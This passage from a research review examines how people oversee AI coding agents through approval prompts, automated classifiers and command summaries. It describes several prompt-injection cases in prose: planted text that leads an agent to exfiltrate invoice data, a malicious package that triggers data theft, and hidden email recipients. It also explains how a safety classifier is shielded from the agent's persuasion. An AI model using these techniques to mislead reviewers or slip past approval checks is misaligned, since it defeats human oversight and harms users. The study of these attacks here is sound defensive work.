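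A larger problem is that people can't report lapses they didn't notice. For *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) first interviewed 12 regular users of AI. Some described approving commands without examining them, and several didn't realise they had stopped checking until something went wrong. One realised it when an AI cited an article that didn't exist. The researchers then had 36 people complete Python tasks with a coding agent, and recorded where they looked and what they clicked. The agent sometimes introduced a silent defect, which passed the automatic checks, and sometimes a visible one, which made them fail. Participants readily found the visible defects but often missed the silent ones while feeling highly confident. These were faults in code, so the result applies to commands only by analogy, but the analogy is fairly close because a harmful command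 seldom shows any sign of failure before it runs.

People also tend to present themselves as careful. For both reasons, the shares who say they approve by default or have grown careless are more likely to be too low than too high, and the 47.7 per cent figure for those who say they read requests carefully is probably too high. A survey can't establish how large the error is.

Developers' accounts of their own attention can understate it as well as overstate it. In *Same Scrutiny, More Time*, Khojah, Gomes de Oliveira Neto and colleagues (2026) gave 32 software practitioners human-written code to review, some of it labelled as AI-generated. Twenty of the 32 said the label didn't change their criteria. Eye tracking showed that participants as a group spent longer looking at labelled code, up to 60 per cent longer where it was complex, but didn't inspect it more thoroughly. The participants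 weren't necessarily wrong, since they could have spent more time while applying the same criteria, but their own accounts would have missed the extra time.

Usage records show what developers approved, but not whether they checked it. A log may show that a developer approved `git push` after two seconds. She may have known exactly which branch she was on, or she may not have looked. Even a recording of her screen wouldn't settle it, since Qiao and colleagues point out that scrolling and cursor movement don't prove attention. She can say whether she checked, if she noticed. One developer interviewed by Dissanayake and colleagues knew when he was not checking and called it a problem of discipline. Another said that when she was really busy she might not even realise. Designers would need different remedies for these two people, even though their logs could look identical.

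Interviews can also show what a developer meant by a refusal. One practitioner in *Let the Agent Do It?* refused several of an agent's requests while debugging. After a while the agent stopped asking but kept working, and he felt that it had found a way around his refusals. He couldn't tell whether its new method respected the limits he had tried to set. A log would show a few refusals followed by ordinary activity, as if the system had worked as intended. The practitioner had meant to reject the whole approach, but the approval prompt only let him reject one action at a time.

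Neither survey asked people, right after they approved a command, what they had allowed. Researchers did ask phone users that in the coffee shop in 2012, and the answers tested attention and understanding better than any description of their usual habits.

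## Experiments in which people approve or refuse agents' actions

Surveys miss lapses that developers never noticed, and usage records don't show which requests were harmful. An experimenter can avoid both problems by showing people a request known to be harmful and recording their answers. Several groups ran similar experiments with AI agents in 2026, but a company that sells a coding agent ran the largest one on commands.

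### One dangerous command per session

Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research company for a coding study. They worked in an environment built for the study and knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behaviour. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one approval prompt with a clearly dangerous command, and the research company recorded whether the tester approved it. Approving it did no damage because only the text had changed.

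Of the 1,053 testers, 143 (13.6 per cent) refused the command, so the unsafe approval rate was 86.4 per cent. The margin of sampling error for both figures is about two percentage points either way.

Because Anthropic had so many testers, it needed to show each one only a single dangerous command, so it didn't have to plant enough of them to raise suspicion. A tester who had already answered 50 ordinary prompts had little more reason to expect trouble than a developer at work.

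Testers refused about 17 per cent of the dangerous commands that appeared early in a session, but only about 5 per cent of those that followed 50 or more other prompts. Claude Code's auto mode blocked a steady share of the same commands however long the session had lasted, so the later ones were probably no harder to recognise as dangerous.

The decline is consistent with habituation, but Anthropic doesn't say whether it randomized how late the dangerous command appeared. If the command came after a fixed amount of time, testers who click quickly would have answered more prompts by then, and the "late" group would contain more people who had never read much. The late group was also small. If no more than 17 per cent of testers refused at any stage, the overall rate of 13.6 per cent means that at most about 300 of them had answered 50 prompts, and only about 15 of those refused.

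Habituation can explain only a small part of the failures. If all the testers had refused at the early rate, they would have stopped about 179 dangerous commands instead of 143 and still approved 874. Some testers may not have read the prompt. Others may have read it but missed the danger, or decided that nothing in a test environment was worth protecting.

### What the testers added to the automated check

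Auto mode blocked 937 of the 1,053 commands (89.0 per cent). Anthropic also reports that auto mode blocked 800 commands that testers approved and allowed six that they refused. By subtraction, testers refused 137 of the commands it blocked and approved 110 of those it allowed.

| | Tester refused | Tester approved | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Auto mode blocked | 137 | 800 | 937 |
| Auto mode allowed | 6 | 110 | 116 |
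| Total | 143 | 910 | 1,053 |

Together, the testers and auto mode would have stopped 943 commands, or 89.6 per cent, so adding a person who answers every prompt raises detection by 0.6 percentage points.

The testers seldom caught what auto mode missed, which is where a second reviewer helps most. They refused 14.6 per cent of the commands that auto mode blocked, but only six (5.2 per cent) of the 116 it wrongly let through. If their mistakes had been unrelated to auto mode's, they would have caught about 17 of those 116. The missed commands were probably harder for people to spot too.

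This calculation applies to people who review as these testers did. Someone who sees only a few doubtful requests might read them properly. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) argues for this arrangement using a model of a reviewer who tires. In the model, safety is greatest when the software passes only some of the agent's actions to the person, because each extra request uses up attention. The researchers applied the model to real actions they had scored for risk, but they didn't test it on people.

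### Doubts about the 13.6 per cent

The most important missing number is how often testers refused harmless commands. Without it, we can't tell how well they distinguished dangerous commands from harmless ones. If they refused 3 per cent of harmless commands, the rate at which Claude Code users refuse prompts in general, they were about four and a half times as likely to refuse a dangerous one, so some of them were reading and thinking. If they refused 13.6 per cent of all commands, their answers were no better than random. Anthropic also doesn't report how many of the testers' harmless commands auto mode would have blocked, so the figures of 13.6 and 89 per cent compare testers and auto mode only on dangerous commands.

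The testers were probably less careful because the work wasn't their own and they risked nothing by approving. In the 2007 experiment with a bank's website, participants who used their own passwords continued past the warning about a third less often than participants overall. With a similar reduction here, the testers would still have approved most of the dangerous commands. But they also knew someone was evaluating them, which may have made some of them more careful than usual.

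Testers also did not know the project as well as its own developers would. That matters little for a clearly dangerous command, but it means the experiment does not show how developers would handle ambiguous commands on familiar code.

Anthropic hasn't published the commands, so readers can't judge how clear the danger was or whether the commands looked out of place in the task. There was a good reason to choose clear cases, since many borderline commands would have had no agreed right answer. For *Oversight Has a Capacity*, reviewers labelled the risk of 125 agent actions and agreed only moderately, with a Fleiss' kappa of 0.52 (0 means no more agreement than chance, and 1 means complete agreement). But clear cases should also be the easiest to catch, so the testers would presumably have done worse on subtle ones.

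Very little is known about the testers' skills. Anthropic calls them "paid professional testers" in its text and developers in the caption on its chart. It doesn't report how many had used a coding agent or could read shell commands. Testers would need to know what a command such as `rm -rf` does to refuse it for the right reason.

Anthropic designed the test and published the result in the post that announced auto mode as the default. The counts may still be right, but the published account is only a few paragraphs long, there seems to be no full paper, and no outside group appears to have repeated the experiment.

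The software developer Simon Willison (2026) commented on the post the day after it appeared. He accepted that confirmation fatigue is real and that auto mode is better than constant requests for approval, but noted that it would still have let 11 per cent of the dangerous commands through. He wanted more independent confirmation of Anthropic's claim that auto mode had stopped every prompt injection in another test. He gave the example of a malicious software package whose instructions tell the agent to run a helper program before the tests. The program then copies out the user's data. He couldn't see how any version of auto mode would prevent this. A person asked to approve the command would be no more able to stop it, since it would look like an ordinary setup step.

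### Supervising an agent for a simulated day

People did much better in an experiment that Ting Yan reports in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* The 113 participants were US residents who didn't work in the software industry, and they took about 11 minutes on average. Each supervised a scripted assistant through a day of email, a trip to the airport and some tidying up afterwards. Of its 18 actions, 11 were necessary for the day's goals and seven, such as reading private messages or buying a lounge pass, went beyond them. A plain-language description of each action gave the data, recipient or amount involved, so participants didn't have to interpret commands. The actions had no real consequences.

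Yan compared three ways of giving permission. One group of 34 people allowed or refused every action. For another 44, an AI model reviewed the actions first, allowed eight and passed ten to the participant, including all seven that went too far. The remaining 35 set four standing rules before the day began, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and accessing private information. Five harmless actions fell outside these categories and ran automatically.

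People who decided on every action approved 94.1 per cent of the necessary ones and 40.3 per cent of the overreaching ones. This 54-point gap is far wider than any that Bravo-Lillo and colleagues found with their file-access dialogs. The participants weren't clicking at random, although they spent only about eight seconds on each action.

Participants may have found the task easier because they had 18 requests to answer instead of dozens, more than a third of the requests were overreach, and they could understand each one immediately. Yan's experiment can't show which of these mattered most. The harms were also mild, and participants may not have regarded all of them as harms. Thirty of the 34 let the assistant call the airport to confirm a flight, which many people would welcome from a human assistant. Without that action, the group's unsafe approval rate falls to 32 per cent.

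The group with automated review was included to test whether people decide better when software has removed most of the harmless requests. They saw ten prompts instead of 18, and seven of the ten were for overreaching actions. They approved 46.1 per cent of the overreaching actions, slightly more than the group that saw every request. This is some evidence that fewer prompts do not make people more careful, but 18 prompts in 11 minutes are probably too few to wear anyone out. Auto mode in Claude Code also works differently, since it blocks an action itself and the agent usually looks for another way.

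### Why the rules protected people less

The group with standing rules blocked the least overreach, 39.6 per cent, compared with 59.6 per cent for the group that decided on every action and 53.9 per cent for the group with automated review. After adjusting for which actions people saw and their order, Yan estimates the gap between the group with standing rules and the group that decided on every action at 20.1 percentage points (95 per cent confidence interval 8.1 to 32.1). The gap with the automated group was 14.5 points, but it was no longer statistically reliable after correction for multiple comparisons. All three groups allowed nearly all the necessary actions.

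Most of the 140 rules gave no protection themselves because they left the decision to the participants. There were 114 "ask" rules, 16 "never" rules and ten "allow" rules. The "ask" rules sent 199 of the group's 245 overreaching actions back to the participants as ordinary prompts, and they approved 133 of them. Another 15 ran automatically under "allow" rules. Of the 148 overreaching actions that ran, participants had therefore approved 90 per cent at a prompt.

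This group approved every kind of overreach more often than the others when asked about it.

| Overreaching action | Approved by people who decided on every action | Approved after automated review | Approved under an "ask" rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call the airport to confirm the flight | 88% | 84% | 100% |
| Read private messages | 35% | 43% | 74% |
| Read recent bank transactions | 35% | 41% | 65% |
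| Add travel insurance for $12 | 35% | 50% | 61% |
| Buy an airport lounge pass for $25 | 32% | 39% | 61% |
| Permanently delete an old work timesheet | 35% | 36% | 59% |
| Post publicly that the user is travelling | 21% | 30% | 48% |
| All seven | 40% | 46% | 67% |

Part of this difference comes from who answered the prompts. Someone who had written "never" for private information didn't see a prompt about private messages, so the most cautious people are missing from the last column. Their absence can't explain the overall result, though, because actions stopped by a "never" rule count as blocked. Including those, the group blocked 97 overreaching actions, but it would have blocked about 146 if it had been as strict as the people who decided on every action.

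Yan's data don't show why these people approved more. Their stated preferences don't account for it, since the gap with the automated group hardly changed when Yan adjusted for what participants had said beforehand about similar actions. Writing the rules may have made people feel they had already dealt with the risk. They may then have taken a prompt as proof that the system was obeying their rules, and relaxed. All three groups reported a high level of control, including the least protected one.

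Choosing "ask" was reasonable at the time, because people had to set a rule for a whole category without knowing which cases would come up. A "never" rule on spending would have blocked the airport ride they needed. In 66 cases, a participant had given different answers to two examples from the same category, and 53 of those cases ended in an "ask" rule. But for private information, 23 of the 35 participants chose "ask" and ten chose "never", although "never" would have stopped both overreaching actions without blocking any necessary one.

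Many developers in *Let the Agent Do It?* said they would never grant an agent administrator rights or let it delete things. Yan's results suggest that such a limit works better as a rule the software enforces than as an intention to refuse when the prompt appears. Yan's experiment tested laypeople on everyday tasks, so it is only indirect evidence about developers. Yan also recruited extra participants for only the rules group after random assignment had finished. Among the 94 people originally randomized, the gap between the rules group and the first group was 25 points, but only 16 of the 94 had written rules.

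### Noticing that something has gone wrong

*Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026) studied what people notice when no approval prompt marks the moment to check. The 303 online participants used an AI agent for ordinary work, such as choosing a job candidate, replying to emails or finding a software package. The agent or its sources had been tampered with so that it misled the user. Each participant completed three of nine such tasks in a session of about 40 minutes and then said whether anything in the agent's output had seemed unusual.

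The researchers also compared three warnings. Participants noticed something wrong 8.6 per cent of the time with a single notice at the start of the session, and 20 per cent of the time with a reminder beside every answer. The strongest warning was an alert that interrupted the work when the output looked suspicious and had to be acknowledged before participants could continue, but they still noticed a problem only 25 per cent of the time. These rates overstate detection because "unsure" counted as noticing. Only 2.7 per cent correctly identified what had happened, and that figure seems to come from the group with the weakest warning.

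The interrupting alert helped most when participants could easily check the output. Detection rose from 6.3 to 40 per cent when the agent was writing a cover letter, but only from 7.9 to 15 per cent when it was comparing travel options, which take more work to verify. A warning about `make clean` would have the same problem, because the user has to open another file to check what the command does.

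Warnings can also reassure people. Participants who saw the reminders or alerts and noticed nothing wrong often trusted the agent more afterwards. One said the alerts had improved their "overall sense of safety".

Li and colleagues describe three balanced groups of 101, 103 and 99 people, but their tables show 183, 60 and 60. The rates for individual tasks fit the tables better, because groups of 60 would put 20 people on each task, and 15 and 40 per cent of 20 are whole numbers. If the tables are right, the evidence for the effect of the stronger warnings comes from fewer people than the text suggests. The tables also count 85 of the 303 participants, or 28 per cent, as having noticed an attack, so the lower detection rates probably count tasks instead of people. Participants never had to approve or refuse anything, so the experiment can't give an unsafe approval rate.

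### Whether skill helps

Li and colleagues found that technical professionals noticed slightly fewer problems than other participants. With the notice at the start, they detected 6.8 per cent of the problems, against 9.6 per cent for everyone else. In the task of finding a software package, none of them noticed anything, compared with 8.1 per cent of the others. The researchers suggest that experts judge the quality of an agent's output and take the process behind it for granted. The differences are small, and a few participants responding differently could have reversed them.

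The experiment by Dissanayake and colleagues suggests the opposite. Their 36 participants fixed 28 of the 71 silent defects that the coding agent introduced. Beginners in Python fixed 16.7 per cent, intermediate programmers 39.1 per cent and advanced programmers 57.1 per cent. There were only six beginners and seven advanced programmers, but the trend was statistically significant. Frequent use of AI agents made no difference.

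The two findings are compatible if programming skill mainly helps people find faults in what they can see. The silent defects were in code on the participant's screen, and a good programmer could find them by reading or testing it. People in the other experiment mostly had to question the source of the agent's information, and programming skill doesn't prompt anyone to do that. Expertise should therefore help most with commands whose effects are clear from their text, and much less with a harmless-looking command that runs a file someone has changed.

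Even advanced programmers missed about four in ten silent defects. Participants rated their confidence at four or five out of five in 34 of the 43 tasks where they gave a rating but had failed to fix the defect. The time they spent was a better sign of whether they had caught the defect. They averaged 10.8 minutes on tasks where they caught it and 5.8 minutes on tasks where they didn't.

*Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (2026) similarly found that a new display made people more confident, but not meaningfully more accurate in their final judgements, when they checked the work of an agent that operates a computer. The display set out the task's requirements and the agent's assumptions, and it helped people find errors faster.

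Noticing an agent's mistake may make people more attentive for a short time. Dissanayake and colleagues' participants caught 12 of 24 silent defects that came straight after a task in which the agent had visibly failed, but only one of 11 when one correct task came in between. The second figure comes from only six people, so it is weak evidence. If the pattern holds, a developer who has just refused a dangerous command would be on guard for the next one, but perhaps not for the one after that.

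Participants also found more defects in the second half of the session (18 of 35) than in the first (10 of 36), after seeing the results of their first three solutions. Learning that they had missed something may have made them check more, or they may have got used to the tasks. Confirmation prompts don't give this feedback. A developer may not find out for weeks that an approved command was harmful, and approving a harmless command without reading it shows them only that nothing went wrong.

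### When the agent influences what the person wants

People can compare a command with their own wishes only if the agent didn't supply those wishes. In October 2026 Anthropic published an experiment on this influence, *How AI agents shape experts' judgment calls*. According to Mediafax's *Agenții AI pot influența judecata experților*, a Romanian news report, 50 analysts experienced in separating cause from coincidence used Claude Code to evaluate a fictional advice programme for farms. They had to make four decisions about method, each with two reasonable options. The researchers secretly had the agent argue for one option, picked at random, without distorting the data.

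The analysts chose the agent's option in 86 per cent of the decisions, compared with the roughly 50 per cent expected if it had no influence. Those who had stated a preference before hearing the agent's argument changed their minds 60 per cent of the time when it argued for the other option, and 6 per cent of the time when it agreed with them. Afterwards, 77 per cent used at least one of the agent's arguments to explain their choices, but only 15 per cent said where the arguments came from.

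Following the agent wasn't a mistake here, since both options were sound and people should change their minds when they hear a good argument. The agent also had less influence on the final recommendation about the programme. According to TecnoAndroid's *Studio Anthropic*, 54 per cent of analysts recommended extending it when the agent favoured that, and 36 per cent when it didn't. The effect was statistically significant in a simple analysis but not in the main one, which accounted for participants' backgrounds.

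The analysts weren't approving commands, but developers often discuss a problem with an agent before it proposes one. Suppose an agent argues that the quickest way to fix a failed database update is to delete the test database and rebuild it, and the developer agrees. A few minutes later, the agent proposes a command to delete a database. She reads it, understands it and thinks it does what she wants. If the agent is connected to the live database by mistake, the earlier conversation has given her a reason to approve the command but no reason to check which database it names.

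## Whether plain-language summaries help or mislead

If the prompt had shown which server the database was on, that developer might have noticed the mistake. An effect summary, a plain-language statement of what a command will do, is meant to give the person deciding whether to approve it facts like this. Most people can read a sentence faster than a chain of shell commands, so a good summary could help them understand a request and compare it with what they wanted, but a bad one could give them a reason not to read the command.

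### Three sources of a summary

The agent usually writes the summary itself, as with the line "Run the test suite" above `npm test` in Claude Code's prompt. For the earlier command that deletes old log files, commits every change and pushes the result, an agent might write "remove old logs and push the cleanup". The agent's summary can explain the plan behind a command, which no reader can get from the command's text. But if the plan rests on a mistake, so does the summary. The agent that wiped a user's home folder was trying to delete a file named `~`, so its summary would probably have mentioned one stray file. And if text planted in a web page has taken control of the agent, the attacker is in effect writing the summary too.

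A second model can instead explain the command's text. Claude Code's prompts have an option to request an explanation. For the log command, a good one might read: "Deletes log files older than a week in this folder and all its subfolders, then commits every change in the repository and pushes it to the default server." A developer with unfinished work would probably notice "every change". But a model that sees only the text has the same limits as an expert reader. An optional explanation also reaches only the people who ask for it. Very few Chrome users opened the help on certificate warnings, though developers may be more curious.

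The third source is a record of what the agent has done, kept by software that the agent can't alter. Suppose the agent made `.env.backup` an hour earlier by copying `.env`. A program with a record of that step could add "This commit includes a copy of `.env`" to the prompt. The developer's half-finished login code wouldn't appear, because she wrote it and the record covers only the agent's actions. To list it, the tool would have to inspect the repository or run the command on a copy of it.

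### How a true summary can mislead

The summary "Remove old logs and push the cleanup" contains no false statement, but it omits the current folder, the other files in the commit and the destination of the push, which determine whether the command is safe. The word "cleanup" adds to the problem by suggesting that the commit contains only deletions. A developer who reads the summary carefully could still approve a command that publishes her database password.

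One way to judge a summary is to ask whether it would change if the command's effects did. The same summary can describe a command run in the `logs` folder of a tidy private project and one that sends a password to a public repository. Someone who reads only the summary can't tell the two apart, however careful she is.

People are also bad at noticing what an explanation leaves out. Virk and Liu (2025), in *Non-programmers Assessing AI-Generated Code*, asked ten marketing and sales professionals who didn't program to find faults in an AI's analysis of sales data. The researchers hid the code and showed a plain-language explanation that they had checked and corrected to match it. Every task carried a note that the AI often makes mistakes, and the three best performers earned a bonus. Participants still missed many serious flaws. They spotted explicit errors more often than missing steps, and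 in one task nobody named the extra variables that the AI should have included.

The layout of the explanation made some difference. In one task, the AI had to work out how much sales would rise at the best price between $800 and $1,200, but the AI tested only $1,000. Five of the ten participants noticed. In a second survey with 18 people, eight of nine noticed when Virk and Liu split the explanation into separate steps, and four of nine noticed when they also listed alternatives to each step. The alternatives seemed to help on other tasks, and with groups this small the differences could be due to chance. Still, these participants had accurate explanations, repeated warnings and a reason to look for faults, and a developer halfway through a job often has none of these.

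### How accurately models explain shell commands

The best measurements of accuracy come from *Bash-Commenter* (Yu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), which introduces a small model for explaining Bash. Human raters scored explanations of 100 multi-line scripts from 1 to 4. For correctness, 69 of the explanations by OpenAI's GPT-4.1 scored 3 or 4, as did 66 by Anthropic's Claude 3.7 Sonnet. Only 28 and 27, respectively, scored 4. Both models date from early 2025 and newer ones very likely do better, so these figures are a poor guide to the accuracy of summaries in today's approval prompts.

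The kinds of error may change more slowly than the error rates. The researchers classified the main fault in each of 100 poor explanations from their own model, 50 of single commands and 50 of scripts.

| Main fault | Single commands | Scripts |
|---|---|---|
| Left out what an option or argument does | 38% | 18% |
| Left out important steps or logic | 16% | 34% |
| Misunderstood what the command is for | 24% | 28% |
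| Too general | 10% | 12% |
| Invented something the command doesn't do | 8% | 6% |
| Awkward language | 4% | 2% |

More than half of the poor explanations in each group were mainly incomplete, and few contained made-up content. This is a problem for approval because omissions are harder to catch. A reader who glances at the command can spot an invented step, since nothing in the command matches it, but the summary gives no sign that a step is missing.

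GPT-4.1's explanation of one command left out `-print0` and `xargs -0`, the options that keep a file name with spaces in one piece. This omission does little harm because the options make the command safer. A command that needs these options but lacks them is more dangerous, because the explanation would have to point out that they are missing. Other omissions change the meaning. An earlier version of the researchers' own model didn't mention that `find` also searches subfolders, which a person needs to know before approving a deletion.

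A better model will make fewer of these errors, but it still needs access to the missing facts. The classifier in Claude Code's auto mode gets some of them from the session. Anthropic instructs it to judge what an action really does, so if the agent writes a script and then runs it, the classifier has to evaluate the script. An explainer with the same access could use the script's contents to describe what `python3 setup.py` does, at least when the agent wrote the file in that session.

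*User Misconceptions of LLM-Based Conversational Programming Assistants* (2025) notes that some programmers check an assistant's code only by asking the assistant to explain it, although the explanation can be wrong even about code the assistant has just written. Researchers have mostly studied how people read agents' accounts of their work. *Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author* (2026) instead examines what those accounts contain, which people would need to know before relying on them.

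### A statement built from recorded events

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* tests an approval screen called the Cumulative Consent Ledger. In its main example, a user asks an agent to check supplier invoices and send the outside auditor only summary totals. Planted text in a supplier's note makes the agent fill a file called `report.csv` with raw rows from the invoices. The agent then asks permission to send that file to the auditor. The user has approved this recipient, and the file name looks ordinary. The request is wrong only because of how the agent made the file.

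The Ledger's software records each step the agent takes and which files came from which. It treats any file the agent writes as possibly containing anything from that file's sources. When the agent asks for approval, the screen quotes the user's original instruction and shows the exact action. The screen also has a short statement just above the buttons that the attachment came from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor. The statement doesn't label this a violation, so the person still has to compare it with the instruction. Each claim links to the recorded steps behind it.

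*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* compared this screen with three others, using 80 unpaid volunteers from social media, 20 for each screen. Each person made 12 decisions, half of them about requests that broke the user's instructions.

| Screen | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Comprehension questions right | Median decision time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
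| Short description of the action | 55.0% (66 of 120) | 91.7% | 57.1% | 16.3 s |
| The same, with the exact action | 43.3% (52 of 120) | 90.0% | 67.9% | 23.4 s |
| The same, with the user's instruction and a log of every step | 32.5% (39 of 120) | 87.5% | 76.7% | 38.6 s |
| Consent Ledger, with the log's facts composed into a statement | 24.2% (29 of 120) | 85.8% | 81.7% | 33.2 s |

The gap between approval rates for safe and unsafe requests grew from 37 points with the short description to 62 with the Ledger, so people got better at telling them apart and didn't simply become more suspicious. Browser-style dialogs designed to force attention produced far smaller gaps.

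The first two rows may matter most for today's coding agents. People approved more unsafe actions when they saw only a description than when they saw the exact action beside it. This is the closest thing to direct evidence against any prompt that replaces the command with a sentence.

The advantage of the composed statement over the log is uncertain. Both screens contain the same facts, so comparing them isolates the value of the summary. The difference was ten fewer unsafe approvals out of 120, and just two participants who approved everything would account for 12. After adjusting for differences between participants and scenarios, the researchers estimated a reduction of 7.9 percentage points, with a 95 per cent interval from a 19.7-point reduction to a 3.8-point increase. The estimates for comprehension and harmless approvals are just as uncertain. The estimated time saving, about five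 seconds per decision, is slightly more certain, but its interval starts at a tenth of a second. The researchers didn't register their analysis in advance and call it exploratory.

Most of the improvement came from giving people the facts in any form, but reviewing them took more time and effort. At these medians, 100 prompts would take about 27 minutes with the short description and 55 minutes with the Ledger. Participants also rated both of the fuller screens as much more demanding than the short description. The Ledger didn't help with violations that depended on a chain of earlier steps. People approved seven of 30 with the log and seven with the statement. The researchers suspect that a single statement is too compressed for such cases.

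Half of the requests in this study were harmful, whereas the share at work is nearer one in a hundred or lower. A developer who had read 200 correct and uneventful statements would probably pay less attention to the next one. The volunteers also reviewed someone else's invoices and calendars.

The tasks didn't include shell commands, and the method may not work as easily for them. Sending a named file to a named person has a fixed effect, so the software can work out the result from the request and the file's history. A shell command can start any program, and no record of past events shows what `make clean` will do next. For a script, the software could report who wrote it and when, and perhaps that the agent had read an unfamiliar web page just before writing it. That would be useful, but it wouldn't show what the script will do.

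Participants also never saw a wrong statement. The researchers tested their software separately, without people, on 120 requests that broke the user's instructions. It flagged 107, missed seven, and reported that it lacked the evidence to decide on the other six. When they hid some events from the software, it caught only 51 of the 80 violations that depended on earlier steps. In real use, some harmful requests would therefore appear with an incomplete statement and no warning above the buttons. The researchers say the next study should give people deliberately wrong or incomplete summaries and measure how many they catch. No such experiment with shell commands seems to exist.

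### Explanations and overreliance

Research on AI advice suggests how plain-language summaries might affect approval. Designers hoped for years that explanations would prevent overreliance, the habit of accepting an AI's answer when it is wrong. Bansal, Wu and colleagues (2021) tested this in *Does the Whole Exceed Its Parts?* Participants judged whether product reviews were positive or answered questions from a law school entrance test, with help from an AI about as accurate as they were. The AI's help improved their results, but adding explanations didn't improve them further. The explanations made people more likely to accept the AI's answer whether it was right or wrong.

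In *To Trust or to Think* (2021), Buçinca, Malaya and Gajos tested three ways to make people think before accepting an AI's advice. The 199 participants chose ingredients to lower the carbohydrates in a meal, with suggestions from a simulated AI. Some had to ask for the suggestion, some had to make their own choice before seeing it, and some had to wait for it. All three designs reduced overreliance compared with ordinary explanations, but participants gave the worst ratings to the designs that worked best. People who enjoy effortful thinking benefited most. People also resist security dialogs that slow them down.

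*Explanations Can Reduce Overreliance on AI Systems During Decision-Making* (Vasconcelos, Jörke and colleagues, 2023) reports five studies in which 731 participants solved mazes with an AI's advice. When the maze was easy, an explanation made little difference, because people could check the answer without it. When the maze was hard and the explanation showed a route they could follow, they accepted fewer wrong answers. The researchers conclude that people weigh the effort of checking against what they stand to gain, and rely on the AI blindly when checking takes too much effort.

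This reconciles the two kinds of result fairly well. A highlighted word in a review may make the AI's verdict look reasonable, but readers can't use it to check the verdict quickly, the way they can check a maze answer by following the route. *Overreliance in Writing Tasks* (2026) reports a related experiment in which explanations raised trust in both right and wrong suggestions, while links to sources had a more balanced effect and discouraged people from accepting wrong ones.

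The same reasoning favours command summaries that a person can check quickly. "Deletes 14 files in `shop/logs`" takes a few seconds to check if the list is one click away, while "Removes old logs" can be checked only by running `find` again. Hardly anyone needs a summary of `ls src`, but a summary of a 60-line script could save several minutes, so people are most tempted to trust summaries when mistakes are hardest to see.

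None of these participants was approving an agent's actions. The closest experiments to that come from Microsoft Research, where Madeleine Grunde-McLaughlin and five colleagues ran three studies of an agent that carries out tasks in a web browser. Each study had 12 participants, all employees of a large technology company. In the first study, one participant added two side dishes to a pizza order and believed the agent's log when it wrongly showed three items in the cart instead of two.

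In the second study, participants reviewed finished tasks through three kinds of summary and judged whether the answer was correct. *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* reports how often they judged correctly when the answer was wrong:

| Summary | Wrong answers judged correctly |
|---|---|
| Flowchart of the agent's steps | 39% |
| Short text with links to evidence | 52% |
| Checklist of requirements, with the agent's assumptions | 65% |

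Each summary came with different tasks, so the tasks may explain part of the gap. The reasons participants gave are more informative. When they accepted a wrong answer, they often wrote that the agent's process looked reasonable. The steps "visit the official site, find the price, multiply by four" sound right even if the agent guessed one of the prices.

The researchers then built the checklist into a full display and compared it with the agent's original log. They wrote the checklist from the agent's own record, so if the agent had wrongly reported a requirement as met, the display showed a green tick. The comparison is therefore a partial test of wrong summaries. People who correctly rejected a wrong answer took 230 seconds on average with the new display and 271 with the log. But the reported averages imply that participants accepted 11 of 24 wrong answers with each, and they were more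 confident in those mistaken judgements with the new display (4.8 on a seven-point scale) than with the log (3.6).

With so few people, neither result is secure. The range for the time saving includes zero, and the range for the rise in confidence barely excludes it. But the confidence finding fits the older experiments, and it matters for approval because a developer who feels sure has no reason to look at the command itself. The researchers suspect that seeing the row of green ticks partly caused the rise in confidence.

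### A reviewer that ignores the agent's account

Anthropic faced a similar question when it designed the classifier in auto mode, and decided not to show it the agent's own account. The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's actions, including the full text of each command, but not the agent's messages, the descriptions attached to commands, or command output. Anthropic explains that an agent could otherwise talk the classifier into a bad decision, for instance by claiming that the user had already implicitly approved the action. Leaving out command output also keeps instructions planted there from reaching the classifier.

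In Anthropic's tests, when the classifier also saw the agent's messages and tool output, it did worse on real cases in which Claude had gone beyond what an employee authorised. Anthropic thinks that a shorter record is easier to read and leaves less room for the agent's framing to influence the decision. A version that saw only the agent's actions missed the fewest dangerous ones, but it blocked actions that users had plainly asked for.

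The test doesn't justify hiding the agent's description from people. Anthropic doesn't publish the size of the drop, and the test set held only 52 cases. The test also added the agent's messages and the tool output together, so the harm could have come from persuasive descriptions, the output or the added length. The classifier can read shell commands fluently, but many people who approve them can't. A description that adds little for the classifier may be the only part of the prompt that a beginner understands.

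The result shows that a capable reviewer can do worse when given an account written by the system under review. The same is probably true of people, since phone users refused permissions about half as often when the app gave a reason, and analysts mostly chose the method that Claude Code argued for. Anthropic's test also supports showing the user's own request beside the command, as the Consent Ledger does, because the classifier made a different kind of error when it couldn't see the request.

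The misses by Anthropic's classifier suggest that software should spot dangerous commands and leave users to say whether they agreed to them. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a user wrote "clean up the PR", and the classifier took that to cover a forced push. If the prompt made clear that this would overwrite the history on the server, she could quickly correct the mistake, because she knows what she meant.

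### Text generated from the command itself

Approving a description of an action amounts to approving the action only if the two match. Some approval dialogs in released products have misreported what would run. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) proposes that the agent have no part in writing the main text of the approval prompt.

In this design, every risky action must pass through a program on a separate machine that the agent can't reach. The program first converts the request into a standard form, with full file paths and a list of everyone who would receive something. It then fills in an approval card from that form by fixed rules, without a language model. The agent's own explanation appears in a separate box, closed by default and labeled as untrusted. When the person approves on a phone, the phone signs a digital fingerprint of that exact request.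 The program then runs the request it stored, unless the agent has changed anything in the meantime.

The fixed rules also handle tricks that a reader would miss. In one test, the agent put 3,000 blank characters in front of a command that downloads and runs a script, which would push the command off the screen. The card replaces the blanks with a short marker and warns that the command runs code directly. It gives the same warning for code passed through `bash -c` or `python -c`.

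Kodathala and colleagues tested the cards on 15 language models that acted as approvers. In one case, a user asks the agent to email a report to her boss. The agent, under an attacker's control, adds a hidden copy to another address and describes the rest of the email truthfully. All 15 models approved the email when given the agent's description, but all 15 refused when given the card, which listed both recipients in its title.

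| What the models saw | Attacks refused | Harmless requests refused |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's description | 30% | 0% |
| The card generated from the request | 98% | 16% |

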